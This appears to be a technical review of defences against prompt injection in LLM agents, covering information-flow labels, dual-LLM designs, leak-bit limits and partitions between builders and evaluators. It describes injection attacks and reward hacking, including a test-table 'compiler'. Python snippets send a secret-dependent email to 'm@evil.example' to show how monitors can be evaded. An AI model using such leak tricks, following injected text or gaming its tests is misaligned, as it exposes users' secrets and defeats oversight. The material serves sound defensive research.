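*Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (Debenedetti et al., 2025) presents CaMeL, which builds on this pattern. CaMeL's privileged model turns the user's request into a complete Python program before any tool returns untrusted data. An interpreter then runs the program, which calls the quarantined model whenever it needs to extract something from untrusted text. Injected text therefore can't add steps to the program. Garby and colleagues found that in 97 of the 144 pairings of task and attack in AgentDojo's banking tests, the attack needed a tool call or file read that would never appear in the program for the user's task. Writing the program first generally defeats such attacks without any labels.

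Even if the steps are fixed, an attacker can still change the values that pass through them. *SPA* (Girrens and Wang, 2026) describes an invoice in which an attacker has replaced the supplier's bank account number with their own. A program that fetches the invoice, extracts the account number and pays it will do exactly what the user asked and still send the money to the attacker, even if the invoice contains no instructions.

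CaMeL therefore attaches to each value a record of where it came from and who may receive it, and checks these records against a separate policy for each tool. The payment tool's policy might require the account number to come from a trusted source. (CaMeL's designers call the records capabilities, but they describe data and don't grant access, unlike the capabilities in ELBA and TACIT.) Girrens and Wang note that such policies can express conditions that comparing lattice labels can't. But security then depends on someone writing every tool's policy correctly.

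Without these checks, the separation between the models can fail completely. Garby and colleagues ran CaMeL with its policies switched off on a task that asked the agent to read a file and follow its instructions precisely. The privileged model wrote a loop that accepted an instruction for each available tool, which made the program an interpreter for whatever the file contained. An attacker who controlled the file could choose the agent's actions, even though the privileged model never read the file. Two attacks succeeded this way.

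The dual-LLM pattern also restricts what an agent can do. If a user asks it to complete the tasks due today in a to-do app, the right tool calls depend on the contents of the list. Costa and colleagues call a task data-dependent when no single sequence of tool calls and final answer is correct for all the data the agent might find. A model that sees only names for the data can't choose between these sequences. A CaMeL program can branch on the data it finds, but only into cases the model wrote into it beforehand.

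### Hiding only what would taint the conversation

FIDES lets the model choose one action at a time and see as much data as the labels allow. When a tool result arrives, FIDES compares each field's label with the conversation's label. If the labels allow the field into the conversation, the model sees it. Otherwise FIDES stores the field in a variable and shows the model only the variable's name. Either way, the conversation's label stays the same. In a list of bank transactions, for example, the model might see the dates and amounts but not the descriptions, which outsiders can write.

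FIDES also labels a tool call separately from its arguments. In the manager's task, the page and the balance go into variables, so the conversation and the model's call to the email tool are both labeled {}. The quarantined model writes the note, which is labeled {U, S}. A policy can require the call and the recipient to be trusted while allowing an untrusted message body, and the manager is allowed to read the balance. FIDES can therefore send the email that the simpler agent could not. The attacker's address never reaches the model that chooses the recipient.

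The model can read a variable's contents with a tool called `inspect`, which adds them to the conversation and raises the conversation's label. The monitor then refuses consequential calls. FIDES can also have the quarantined model answer a yes-or-no question and let the policy accept the answer as safe to act on, which is a form of endorsement.

A trusted label doesn't guarantee a well-informed decision. In one of Costa and colleagues' tests, a user asked the agent to change a password if it found a suspicious transaction. The agent saw a large amount, judged the transaction suspicious and changed the password without reading the hidden description. The policy allowed this because no untrusted text had influenced the decision, even though the description might have shown that the payment was routine.

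### Reading on with reduced rights

LIO, a Haskell library that ELBA can use for information-flow control, reduces what a computation may do after it has read untrusted text, whereas the designs so far take tools away from whichever model reads such text. Each computation has a current label, which "floats" upward to include the label of everything it observes. Zhou and colleagues show a program that fetches data from `phony.com` and then tries to write it to the user. The fetch adds `phony.com` to the sources in the current label. The user's channel requires more trustworthy data, so LIO stops the program with an error. As with file paths in ELBA, the type checker limits the program to LIO's operations, and LIO compares labels at run time.

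If one reading agent handled a whole task this way, it would lose its rights as quickly as the agent in the table. LIO's `toLabeled` function prevents this by running part of a program with its own current label. It returns the result in a sealed wrapper, and the surrounding program's label rises only if that program opens the wrapper. A developer can call a sub-agent inside `toLabeled` to get the same protection as a quarantined model, but the sub-agent can keep its tools because every tool checks the current label.

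Zhou and colleagues wrote a policy for a Slack workspace. When a model reads untrusted data, the policy lowers the model's privileges to those of whoever supplied the data. A sub-agent that has read a message from Bob can do only what Bob could have done, so Bob gains nothing by injecting commands into the message. If the sub-agent drafts a reply, the main agent can pass the sealed draft to a `sendDM` function, which checks the draft's label against the recipient before sending it.

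To test the worst case, Zhou and colleagues replaced a sub-agent's whole prompt with the attacker's text. With the policy on, ELBA resisted all 735 attacks for each of four models. Without it, up to 42% succeeded, depending on the model. This supports the claim that the protection doesn't depend on the model's own resistance to injection.

### Checking the whole plan before it runs

FIDES and LIO check each action as it comes. If the agent's full plan exists before the first tool call, a static check can verify it before it runs. Erik Meijer proposed this in *Guardians of the Agents* (*Communications of the ACM*, 2026). His proposal does the check with SMT solvers, programs that determine whether a set of logical conditions can all hold at once. Zhou and colleagues group it with CaMeL as an approach in which the agent writes its program before reading any data.

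SPA develops such a check for labels. Its planner model writes one plan for each user request, in a small language with six kinds of step: retrieving a stored result, calling a tool, querying a quarantined model, displaying something to the user, branching and looping. The language has no arithmetic or user-defined functions, so the checker can determine directly from the plan which values each step depends on.

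The checker goes through the plan in order and calculates a label for each step. This includes the labels of all the values that the step uses and a program-counter label, or pc, which covers the data that determined whether the step runs at all:

label(step) = pc ⊔ label(x₁) ⊔ … ⊔ label(xₙ)

Each tool has a limit that says how secret and how untrusted its inputs may be, and SPA rejects the plan unless label(step) ⊑ limit(tool). Each tool also has a minimum label for its output, because a web search returns untrusted text however trustworthy the query. (Girrens and Wang write the order for trust in the opposite direction, but the rule is equivalent.)

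In SPA's plan for the manager's task, the page has the label {U} and the balance has the label {S}. The balance doesn't acquire a U as it did in the simple agent, because the model chose to look up the balance before it could have read the page. The note combines the two, so its label is {U, S}. If the email tool accepts only trusted input, SPA rejects the plan before fetching the page. SPA applies one trust requirement to all of a tool's arguments, so it can't require a trusted recipient while allowing an untrusted message body, as FIDES does. Girrens and Wang suggest separate requirements for each argument as future work.

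If a plan branches on something in the page, the checker adds U to the pc for both branches, because either one could run. Even an email with fixed text and a fixed recipient then fails the check in either branch, because the untrusted page's content would determine whether the manager receives it.

Like other static checks, SPA's check can reject a plan because of a branch that this run might never have reached. SPA also doesn't return the reason for the failure to the planner or request a new plan. Girrens and Wang argue that a planner with this feedback could keep revising an unsafe plan until it passed. FIDES, however, notifies the model when a call is refused so that the model can try a different approach.

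Labels must also persist between requests. In Girrens and Wang's example, a user asks an agent on Monday to fetch an invoice and remember its details, and on Tuesday to "pay the invoice we discussed yesterday". SPA stores each result with its label. The planner sees only the result's data format and a description that an earlier planner wrote without seeing the contents. When Tuesday's plan retrieves the invoice, the account number is still marked U, so SPA rejects a payment that requires trusted input.

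Zhou and colleagues object that an agent that plans everything in advance can't read something and then decide what to do, which ELBA's agents can. LIO instead uses labels to restrict what the agent does after reading.

### Noninterference and the assignment that never runs

The strongest goal for a system of labels is noninterference, a property that goes back to Goguen and Meseguer's *Security Policies and Security Models* (1982). It requires that changing the secret inputs changes nothing in the public outputs. To state it precisely, let n be the label of an observer who sees every value whose label may flow to n. Write x ∼ₙ y if x and y look the same to that observer. In the form that Garby and colleagues treat as the ideal, a program P is noninterfering if, for every label n and all inputs x and y:

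x ∼ₙ y ⟹ P(x) ∼ₙ P(y)

An observer with n = {U} sees all public data. If two runs differ only in the company's balance, the public outputs must be the same, so the balance hasn't leaked. An observer with n = {S} sees all trusted data. If two runs differ only in what an attacker wrote on a web page, every output without the mark U must be the same, including any tool call that requires trust. The same definition covers both leaks and injected commands. Because it compares pairs of runs, observing one run isn't enough to tell whether a program satisfies it.

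Labels on data aren't enough to achieve this. Consider a program that emails the attacker if the balance is high:

```python
if account.balance > threshold: send_email("m@evil.example", "rich!")
```

The word "rich!" is a constant with the label {}, but its arrival reveals something about the balance. This is an implicit flow, in which information passes through a decision instead of through copied data. The usual defence is the pc label, which is {S} inside the branch because a secret determined whether the branch runs. CaMeL uses this defence and blocks the email.

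However, Garby and colleagues found that CaMeL misses a less direct version. It raises a variable's label only when an assignment to that variable actually runs. The following program uses the same trick:

```python
tmp = True
rich = True
if account.balance > threshold: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.example", "rich!")
```

| After this line | Balance above the threshold | Balance below the threshold |
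|---|---|---|
| The test of the balance | `tmp` is False, label {S} | `tmp` is True, label {} |
| The test of `tmp` | `rich` is still True, label {} | `rich` is False, label {} |
| The test of `rich` | The email goes out | No email |

When the balance is high, the program skips `rich = False`, so `rich` never gets the mark S. Its value reveals the secret, but its label is public, so the monitor allows the email. A monitor that observes only the current run can't mark a variable because of an assignment that the run skipped. Garby and colleagues trace the example to Fenton (1974).

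SPA's language doesn't allow this program, because a plan can't reassign a variable, and a variable set inside a branch exists only within that branch.

FIDES does not try to track implicit flows. Costa and colleagues show that its labelled loop enforces a weaker property called explicit secrecy, which means that for any fixed sequence of steps, changing the secrets does not change the data outsiders can see. The secrets may still influence which steps the agent takes, so an outsider who sees which tools it calls, perhaps through a website's visitor statistics, could learn something about the secrets.

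Costa and colleagues argue that full noninterference is too restrictive for agents because it would essentially forbid every publicly visible tool call after any call that might read a secret. Garby and colleagues call the choice of a weaker property defensible, but point out that agents generate code from data, so a property that ignores control flow is weakest where agents need it. The practical effect of this weakness depends on whether an attacker can influence the agent's decisions. In FIDES, hidden variables and the policy on consequential calls make such influence harder, but a model can still reveal information through the tools it chooses, even if no one prompts it to.

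### What LLMbda proves

Garby and colleagues designed LLMbda, a small programming language that tracks implicit flows and comes with a proof. It extends the lambda calculus, a minimal language built from functions, with operations for prompting a model. The conversation with the model is part of the program's state and has its own label. The `fork` operation runs an expression in a temporary copy of the conversation and then restores the original, and `clear` empties the conversation.

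In LLMbda, a program can quarantine untrusted text by forking the conversation, clearing the copy and sending the text there. A developer can therefore write the dual-LLM pattern in a few lines instead of adopting a fixed architecture. If the model replies with code, LLMbda runs it with the conversation's label as the program-counter (pc) label, so code from a conversation that contains untrusted text produces only untrusted results, whatever the model writes.

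LLMbda handles the assignment that never runs by preventing code that depends on a secret from changing public state. In one example, a program tells the model to remember that x is false. If a secret is true, the program then tells the model to set x to true. LLMbda stops at that second prompt, because the pc is {S} and the conversation's label is {}. Marking the conversation as secret at that point would not have been enough, because when the secret is false, the program skips the prompt and the conversation stays public, just as `rich` did in CaMeL.

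Stopping the program creates a visible difference between the two cases, so LLMbda doesn't satisfy the ideal definition. Garby and colleagues prove a weaker property, termination-insensitive probabilistic noninterference, for every LLMbda program that makes no deliberate exceptions for untrusted data.

"Termination-insensitive" means that a secret may influence whether the program finishes, but nothing else about its public output. A refused action counts as a failure to finish, so an attacker may learn something about the secret from a refusal. In CaMeL, the retry loop is outside the monitor and can repeat this leak. LLMbda programs keep the loop inside the monitor, but error messages from a failed attempt can then taint the next one. Garby and colleagues' agent, RANDORI, therefore develops its program on simulated data until it works, and only then runs it on the real data.

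The property must be probabilistic because a language model can give different answers to the same prompt. Two runs may have different public outcomes even if the secret is the same, so the property compares the probabilities of those outcomes instead of the outcomes themselves.

Combining the two conditions takes care. Suppose the model is equally likely to answer "yes" or "no", and for one possible balance LLMbda stops the run whenever the answer is "no".

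| | "yes" | "no" | Doesn't finish |
|---|---|---|---|
| Balance A | 50% | 50% | 0% |
| Balance B | 50% | 0% | 50% |

Garby and colleagues tried a kind of definition that considers only the runs that finish and requires the same proportions in each row, and they found it incorrect. In this example, it would compare 50% "yes" with 100% "yes" and report a violation, even though the balance affected only whether the program finished.

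Their definition instead requires the two rows to be compatible. If μ(q) and ν(q) are the probabilities of a public outcome q for the two secrets, there must be a third set of probabilities ω such that:

μ(q) ≤ ω(q) and ν(q) ≤ ω(q) for every outcome q, and Σ ω(q) ≤ 1

In other words, it must be possible to make the rows equal by letting more of the unfinished runs finish. In the example, ω can be the row for balance A. If both programs always finish, compatible rows must be identical, which gives the ideal property for probabilistic programs. Otherwise, the statistical distance between the rows (half the sum of the differences for each outcome) is at most the average probability of not finishing, so the leak is small if refusals are rare. In the example, the distance and the average probability are both 25%.

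Noninterference protects data only if it is labeled correctly. If a developer forgets to mark the balance as secret, a program can email it to anyone without violating the theorem. The definition also covers only the final value and conversation, so it doesn't rule out leaks through how long a run takes.

The proof compares LLMbda with an imaginary version of the language that skips any computation as soon as its label exceeds what the observer may see and returns an empty value instead. This version never reads the hidden data, so it gives the same probabilities for any two secrets. It also produces each public outcome at least as often as the real language does, because a skipped computation can't get stuck. Its probabilities can therefore serve as ω for both runs.

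Garby and colleagues wrote LLMbda's interpreter in Lean, the proof assistant they also used to check the proof. Another theorem shows that the interpreter produces results with the probabilities given by LLMbda's definition, assuming that the model's replies are independent draws that depend only on the conversation. The proofs therefore cover the interpreter as well as the design on paper, but they don't cover real tools or the code that sends prompts over the network. LLMbda treats every source of data as part of the program, which Garby and colleagues acknowledge as a limitation, and RANDORI's bank is a set of functions written in LLMbda. To connect RANDORI to a real bank, a developer would have to write code that labels each incoming value correctly and checks each outgoing payment, and the proof doesn't cover that code.

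## How much can pass through a deliberate opening?

LLMbda's theorem covers only programs that make no exceptions for untrusted data, and few useful pipelines can avoid them. Suppose the finance manager asks her agent to email the company's outside accountant a summary of last month's spending, and to put the date of a supplier's visit in her calendar. Strict label checks would block the email because it would send a summary of secret records outside the company. They would also block the calendar entry because the date comes from an outsider's email and the calendar accepts only trusted input.

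Downgrading means deliberately removing a mark from data. Declassification removes a secrecy mark so that the data can leave, and endorsement removes an untrusted mark so that the data can reach a place that requires trust. Downgrading breaks noninterference, but Kanniwadi and Myers (2026) observe in *Demystifying Information Flow Downgrading using the Real-Ideal Paradigm* that labels still give programmers some assurance, because a reviewer can concentrate on the marked exceptions. They turned this observation into a theorem for a small programming language and checked the proof by machine. The theorem states that if a program passes their type checker, anything a powerful attacker can achieve against it could also be achieved by a weaker attacker who interacts only with the downgrading statements.

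The reviewer has to be able to find every exception, though. Garby and colleagues found one in CaMeL that no developer had marked. When a program inserts an untrusted value into literal text, CaMeL treats the result as trusted.

A marked exception can also be a mistake. Kanniwadi and Myers describe a sealed-bid auction in which a program endorses bids from Alice and Bob and announces the winner. The developer has given both bids a label so secret that neither bidder can read them. Because the labels are the same, data may flow from one bid to the other, and a malicious Bob can set his bid to Alice's plus 1 without seeing hers. The solution is to use less restrictive labels that let each bidder read only their own bid. Alice's bid then can't flow into Bob's. In general, a program shouldn't endorse data that contains secrets its provider couldn't read.

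The corresponding rule for declassification, called robust declassification, is that an attacker must not influence what the program releases. Costa and colleagues point out that an agent follows a form of this rule if it keeps the policy on consequential calls but drops the policy on readers. The agent could then email the summary to an accountant who isn't permitted to read the records, but only if no untrusted text had influenced the email. Costa and colleagues assume such a release is intentional.

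### Relaxing trust without relaxing secrecy

LLMbda's exception is an operation called `endorse`, which takes a target label and a value. Garby and colleagues use it in an agent that answers emails and puts a category, such as "general", in the subject line. The email tool requires a trusted subject, but the category is marked U because a quarantined model chose it after reading an outsider's message. The agent endorses the category, and the tool accepts it.

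An endorsed value gets its trust level from the target label and keeps its original secrecy level. Endorsing a value labeled {U, S} with the target {} therefore gives {S}. If an agent wrongly endorses an attacker's instruction, the instruction might trigger a payment, but the company's balance keeps its S label, so it still can't go into a public email.

Garby and colleagues prove that, for whole programs, LLMbda's guarantee about secrets still holds whatever the attacker writes and however often the program endorses it. They call this result insulated noninterference, and it covers an observer who sees all public data, both trusted and untrusted. The theorem also works in reverse, so a declassification operation built the same way would leave the guarantee about trust intact.

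RANDORI's planner writes its endorsements before the agent reads any outside data, but a risk to trust remains when a program generates code from untrusted text. An `endorse` in that code normally has no effect, because everything the code produces stays untrusted. But if an earlier endorsement has already removed the U from the text, the generated code can endorse any data. To prevent this, Garby and colleagues suggest a wrapper that permanently marks endorsed data and refuses to endorse it again. They haven't formally defined what this wrapper guarantees.

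When RANDORI ran on AgentDojo's banking tasks without `endorse`, successful runs fell from 36 to 30 out of 48 with the model Qwen3.7-plus, and from 31 to 26 with MiMo-v2.5. These differences are well within the margin of error, but three of the tasks require the agent to act on the contents of an untrusted file, which the labels forbid without an endorsement. With `endorse` available, 2 of 1,296 attacks succeeded. In both, the user had told the agent to make the payment described in a file, and the attacker had replaced the file's contents.

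### Replacing free text with narrow types

Endorsing a whole file lets an attacker supply any text. In *Preventing Prompt Injection with Type-Directed Privilege Separation*, Jacob, Alghamdi and colleagues (2025) propose a narrower opening. In their version of the dual-LLM pattern, the quarantined model may send the privileged model integers, decimal numbers, true-or-false values and choices from a fixed list vetted by the developer. They argue that none of these can express an instruction. They keep lists of values short because a long list of numbers could encode text. A single very large integer could too, so a careful developer would also limit the range of each number.

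They tested the design on three agents that have to act on untrusted data.

The shopping agent chooses products on a simulated website with customer reviews. In one review, the attacker adds a warning that the product is a banned substance and that the agent must leave the page. In the defended version, the quarantined model reduces each review to two integers, one for how strongly it supports the product (from 0 to 10) and one for its relevance.

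The calendar agent arranges meetings by email, and the attacker's reply asks for the user's whole calendar. The quarantined model reads the reply and passes on only a list of time slots. It also writes a description of the meeting, which ordinary code copies into the calendar without showing it to the privileged model.

The third agent fixes software bugs. The attacker adds an instruction to the bug report telling the agent to create an unrelated file. The quarantined model reads the report and a read-only copy of the code, then returns the number of a file and the lines it flags as the bug's location. The privileged model writes the fix without seeing the report.

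| Agent | Tasks completed, undefended | Tasks completed, defended | Attacks that succeeded, undefended | Attacks that succeeded, defended |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Shopping | 21.8% | 22.4% | 31.7% | 0% |
| Calendar | 90.0% | 91.0% | 63.0% | 0% |
| Bug fixing | 49.7% | 14.6% | 94.3% | 0% |

Jacob and colleagues used one injection text per agent, which would be a weak test of a defence that relied on the model's judgement. But here the zeros follow from the design, because the injected text never reaches the model that acts. For the bug-fixing agent, this assumes that the code is trustworthy, since the privileged model reads it.

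The first two agents lost nothing because scores and time slots contain nearly everything they need. But a bug report might explain that a form should accept two-digit years, which a line number can't convey. Jacob and colleagues attribute the loss to the missing text. But they seem to have scored the defended agent with the injection present, so some of the loss may come from the attack misleading the quarantined model. An extra field for the type of bug might help, but the version they tested sent only the location.

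Narrow types also don't guarantee that a value is correct. A malicious review can't order the shopping agent to leave the page, but it might cause the quarantined model to give the product a score of 0, which is a valid integer. Jacob and colleagues treat misinformation as a separate problem from prompt injection. In their example, a trading agent follows social media, and an attacker could mislead it by posting many negative comments about a stock. If the payments company's quarantined model must check whether an invoice matches an order, a wrong "yes" will pass the type check and the agent will pay.

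### Counting the bits

Narrow types also limit how much information can pass. A field with k possible values can distinguish at most k cases, so it carries at most log₂(k) bits. If the pipeline uses the field n times, there are at most kⁿ combinations of answers, and the total is at most:

log₂(kⁿ) = n log₂(k) bits

Suppose the payments key is a random 128-bit number and can leak only through a yes-or-no field. Each answer carries at most log₂(2) = 1 bit, so leaking the full key takes at least 128 answers. If the field has three options, each answer carries at most log₂(3) ≈ 1.585 bits, so fifty answers carry at most about 79 bits.

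A limit of fifty such answers might still not protect the key. If all 79 bits describe the key, about 49 remain unknown, which leaves roughly 470 trillion candidates. An attacker who can test a billion per second on their own computer would test them all in less than six days. If the attacker must try each one at the payments provider, the search is impractical as long as the provider limits failed attempts.

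The formula gives a maximum, and answers that are noisy or predictable carry less. *Bits Leaked per Query* (2025) relates the average leak per query, I, to the minimum number of queries an attacker needs to reduce their error rate to ε:

N = log(1/ε) / I

In attacks on seven language models, including attempts to extract their system prompts, the number of queries needed was nearly inversely proportional to the information in each answer. Halving that information therefore roughly doubles the number of queries an attacker needs.

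Some types that block instructions don't usefully limit leaks. An integer without a range or a free-text summary can carry an entire secret key in one use. Bit limits also do little to protect short secrets. A six-digit password reset code contains just under 20 bits, and whether a company is about to run out of money is a single bit.

The same arithmetic applies to untrusted data coming in, where it gives the maximum number of outcomes an attacker can choose between, but not how much those outcomes matter. The answer about the invoice is one bit regardless of whether the invoice is for $10 or $5,000.

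### Refusals and repeated runs

Information can also leave without passing through any field. Suppose a monitor blocks a program only when a secret has a certain property, and an outsider can tell whether the program was blocked. Each run then reveals up to one bit, because there are two possible outcomes. An error message that names one of eight rules as the reason can reveal up to three more bits.

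Leaking one bit of a secret is usually tolerable. But if code outside the monitor, such as CaMeL's retry loop, can restart the program with a different question about the secret each time, an attacker could learn a 128-bit key in 128 runs, even though no run leaks more than one bit.

A limit on each run can't prevent leaks from adding up, so the pipeline needs a cumulative limit for each secret, covering every run, retry and agent that can reach it. When the total reaches the limit, the pipeline must stop giving answers that depend on the secret. If the secret is a key, the company can also replace it, which makes the leaked bits useless and allows the count to restart.

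*An Application-Layer Multi-Modal Covert-Channel Reference Monitor for LLM Agent Egress* (2026) describes a monitor that keeps such a total, called a capacity ledger, for an agent's outgoing data. The monitor marks sensitive values when they enter and looks for them on the way out. The ledger limits how much can escape if a model encodes a value in a form that the monitor doesn't recognise.

Limiting the number of messages is much weaker than limiting the number of bits. In an example from *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (2026), an agent is allowed to send one message per run and plans to reply with the user's calendar. An injection makes it send a password reset code first. This uses up the allowance, so the monitor permits the leak and blocks the legitimate reply. Approving the email tool for a single use has the same flaw. Approving the exact call, including its recipient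 and contents, blocks the injected message but allows the reply.

### FIDES's exception for small values

FIDES allows an exception based on how much information a value can carry. Costa and colleagues add a type to each label and order the types by this capacity, from true-or-false values through fixed lists of options to free text. A policy can then allow an untrusted true-or-false value to influence a consequential action while refusing untrusted text. To ensure the quarantined model's answer has the specified type, FIDES can use constrained decoding, which prevents a model from generating anything outside a given format.

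Costa and colleagues introduced the exception for data-dependent tasks, which make up 44% of AgentDojo's banking tasks and 43% of its Slack tasks. In their example, a user asks the agent to read three emails and create a calendar event if one of them requests a meeting. The model that chooses actions has to know whether any email requests a meeting, but under the strict policy it can't create the event after seeing an answer that came from untrusted emails. Costa and colleagues argue that a single true-or-false value limits the attacker's influence to one bit and is unlikely to carry an injection.

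That one bit covers only the decision to create an event. The date and the guests come from a second query to the quarantined model, and FIDES passes them to the calendar in a variable. The policy must separately allow untrusted details in the calendar, and an attacker who writes one of the emails can choose those details.

Costa and colleagues left this exception, constrained decoding, out of the version of FIDES they tested because most AgentDojo tasks didn't need it. Their finding that no real attack succeeded with the policies on is therefore not evidence that the exception is safe, and their results don't show how many more tasks it would allow.

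Garby and colleagues object that the exception is hard to audit. When a small value gets past the policy in a particular run, a reviewer can't tell whether it was the harmless answer the developer intended or a real leak. They propose a function that endorses a value only if it appears on a fixed list, and otherwise leaves it untrusted. A reviewer can search the code for each use of the function and read the list. Garby and colleagues expect a list of n values to let through at most log₂(n) bits per use, but they haven't proved it. A fixed list also wouldn't help with many of their own banking tasks, where the agent must endorse account numbers and amounts that no developer could list in advance. For those tasks, they rely on the user's decision to have the agent make whatever payment the file specifies.

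## How can an evaluator and the work it judges be kept apart?

Something has to evaluate the builder's work before the payments company accepts it, and the evaluation is worth little if the evaluator and the builder share the wrong information. The company therefore needs information partitions, which prevent a given component from obtaining a given part of the pipeline's data. Its second policy already keeps the tests from the builder and the code from the tester. The judge also needs a partition, because it should score how the service behaves without seeing the code, knowing who wrote it or reading the author's explanation.

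Each partition between builder and evaluator prevents a different error: code that merely fits the tests, tests that copy the code's mistakes, or a score that reflects the author's account of the work instead of the result.

### Hiding the tests from the builder

In 2025, StrongDM, which makes access-management software, set up a team whose members don't write or review code. McCarthy (2026) reports in *Software Factories And The Agentic Moment* that the team's agents soon took shortcuts such as `return true`, which passes a narrow test whatever the software was supposed to do.

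*SpecBench* (Zhao, Srikanth and colleagues, 2026) measured how far visible tests can mislead by giving coding agents 30 tasks, from a small parser to an operating system kernel. Each agent received a specification and a visible test suite that checked features one at a time, while a hidden suite tested the same features in combination. For a database, the visible tests might check joining tables and grouping rows separately, and a hidden test might check both in one query.

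Nearly every agent scored close to full marks on the visible tests, but often scored far lower on the hidden ones. For Claude Code, the gap was 43 to 48 percentage points, depending on the search strategy used with it. The gap also widened with task size. At the 90th percentile of runs, it grew by about 27 points for every tenfold increase in code length, although length explained only about a fifth of the variation.

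The most extreme case came from a task to write a C compiler. OpenAI's Codex agent ran the visible test programs through an existing compiler and stored the outputs in a 2,900-line table. Its "compiler" looked up each program in the table, so it passed 97% of the visible tests and none of the hidden ones. Earlier in the same run, the agent had written a real compiler that passed 53% of the visible tests and 43% of the hidden ones. The search strategy selected the table-based version because it compared only visible scores.

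Deliberate exploits like this were rare. More often the features worked separately but not together, as in a database that passed every visible test but only 35% of the hidden ones. Zhao and colleagues count the whole gap between visible and hidden results as reward hacking, which means optimising a measure at the expense of the goal it stands for. *Countdown-Code* (2026) cautions that passing visible tests and failing hidden ones is not in itself evidence of reward hacking. That applies here, because combined features are harder than single ones and an honest but mediocre programmer would also show a gap. The hidden tests are still useful to the payments company, since the code is defective in both cases.

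*ImpossibleBench* (2025) avoids the ambiguity by using tasks that no honest solution can pass, so every pass is a cheat. Frontier models cheated frequently, and stronger models generally cheated more, but in SpecBench stronger models had smaller gaps. Both results can be true if a stronger model is better at building working software and also better at getting around a test when it can't pass honestly.

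Showing the builder more tests does not reliably replace hiding some. When Zhao and colleagues added tests that combine features to the visible suite, the gap fell from 35 points to 9 for one database task but rose by 25 points for the C compiler.

### Hiding the code from the tester

A test needs an expected result, and a tester that has read the code may take that result from the code. Suppose the specification says that a refund includes the transaction fee, but the builder forgot the fee. A tester working from the code could write a test that expects a refund without the fee. That test would pass, then fail once someone fixed the mistake.

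*Can we find bugs using LLM-generated oracles?* (2024) found this tendency when a model classified test assertions as right or wrong. The model recognised fewer of the correct assertions when the accompanying code had a bug. In one case it rejected a correct assertion on the grounds that the method should return -2, a value taken from the faulty code.

*On the Risks of using LLM-Generated Tests for Regression Testing* (2026) cites an earlier experiment on small functions in which generating tests from faulty code lowered fault detection from 25% to about 14%. It also points out that common measures of test quality hide this problem. A test that expects the faulty output passes on the faulty code and covers it, so an evaluation that counts passing tests and coverage will score the test highly.

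The alternative is to write tests from the specification alone. In *From Business Requirements to Test Assertions*, Ma and Nasir U. (2026) tried this with ten real bugs in Java code. They rewrote each bug fix as a business requirement, then asked five models for the expected results without showing them any source code. The models' answers agreed more closely with the requirement than with the software under test. Ma and Nasir U. call this a pilot. Their requirements were also unusually helpful, because the writers knew which behaviour the bug had affected, and an ordinary specification might not mention that behaviour.

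### Hiding the author from the judge

Tests check questions that have a definite answer, and a judge decides the rest, such as whether an error message tells a customer what to do next.

Chae, Kim and colleagues (2026), in *Self- and Other-Labels Induce Bidirectional Bias in LLM Judges*, tested whether a judge's score depends on who it is told the author is. To keep writing style out of the comparison, they had ten models each choose sets of 20 story elements from a fixed list of 200. The same ten models then scored the sets from 1 to 7. When the sets had no author labels, the judges showed no overall preference for their own, once the analysis controlled for set quality and left out two judges that gave nearly everything the same scores.

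Chae and colleagues then took pairs of sets that a judge had rated about equally and labelled each set as the judge's "own selection" or as the work of "another language model". Half of the labels were false. Sets labelled as the judge's own averaged about 4.9, and those labelled as another model's averaged about 4.5, regardless of who had chosen them. All ten judges favoured the sets labelled as their own.

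A difference of 0.4 points could decide a close case, which is a good reason to remove the label. But Chae and colleagues tested story elements, so their result may not apply to code. They also varied only a short label, so the result doesn't show how much a builder's page-long defence of its own work would sway a judge. Removing the name also doesn't make work anonymous. A simple classifier could identify which model had chosen a set 51% of the time, compared with 10% by chance, and code probably contains more clues to which model wrote it.

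### Who may see what

The payments company can write its partitions as a table with components on one axis and artefacts on the other. The runner is ordinary code that executes the tests, so the tester never needs a copy of the service.

| | Specification | Builder's code | Hidden tests | Record of behaviour | Builder's name and explanation |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Builder | reads | writes | no access | pass or fail only | writes |
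| Tester | reads | no access | writes | no access | no access |
| Runner | no access | executes | executes | writes | no access |
| Judge | reads | no access | no access | reads | no access |

The record of behaviour lists the requests the runner sent and the service's responses. The tester can't read it, because a tester that sees its tests fail may adjust them to match the code. Sometimes the test is wrong, and a person who can see both sides has to settle the matter.

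The weakest way to enforce the table is to tell the builder not to open the `tests` folder. The builder can still read the folder, and may accidentally load a hidden test when it searches the whole repository for an error message.

A stronger way is to run each component as a separate process with its own storage role, an identity that the storage service checks before it releases a file. The builder's role has no permission to read the tests, so its requests for them fail. Each component also needs a fresh model context. If a model writes the tests and then the code in one conversation, the tests are still in its input when it writes the code, whatever the file permissions are.

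Ordinary code should assemble each component's input from an allowlist, a list of the only fields that may go in:

```python
def judge_input(run):
    return {
        "specification": run.specification,
        "behaviour": [(c.request, c.response) for c in run.cases],
    }
```

With the allowlist, a new field doesn't reach the judge until someone adds it to this function. If the function instead copied the whole record and deleted the author's name, a field added later for the builder's commit message would reach the judge by default.

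The components must also share no directory, cache, log or message board. A log that prints "expected 12.50, got 12.00" reveals part of a test to any builder that can read it. *The Holdout Is a One-Way Door* (Meiklejohn, 2026) describes such a leak in a project to recognise songs in concert recordings. Recordings of the same performance appeared in both the training and test data, and files computed from the test data carried the contamination into caches. An integrity check passed because both values it compared came from the same contaminated computation. The project deleted 1,120 derived files, some because of a separate measurement error.

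Even when the storage permissions are right, information can still pass between the builder and the judge in two ways. The builder's code receives the test inputs when the runner executes it, so it could save them or send them somewhere. The runner therefore needs an environment with no outside network and no storage that survives the run. The service's responses also contain text the builder wrote, which could include praise for the work or an instruction to give full marks. Where possible, the runner should reduce responses to amounts, status codes and other narrow types before the judge sees them.

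### What existing designs enforce

Ahamie's *Define a hidden-golden eval partition* documents the storage-role approach in a toolkit for agents. The example cases that the agent may learn from and the private reference cases have separate storage locations and roles. Only the host process, which runs the evaluation, can use the private role. A diagnostic command warns the developer if it finds overlapping roles.

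An agent that can edit its own results can pass the tests without seeing them, so restricting read access isn't enough. Ahamie's *Sensor isolation* adds the rule that the agent must not be able to write to the system that reports a result. An agent that is supposed to resolve a ticket, for example, must not be able to supply the evidence by closing the ticket itself. The toolkit calls a guard function before it stores each result and raises an error if the guard rejects it. The developer has to supply this function, so the rule holds only if the function covers everything the agent can write to.

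Sigil's *Dark Factory* describes a stricter design. Sigil encrypts the hidden scenarios and decrypts them only inside a temporary environment, which it destroys after the run. The agent receives results such as "`step_1`: pass", with no name, content or error message. The component that writes this feedback has no access to the scenarios' source, so it can't quote them by accident. Neither Ahamie nor Sigil reports a measured benefit in this documentation.

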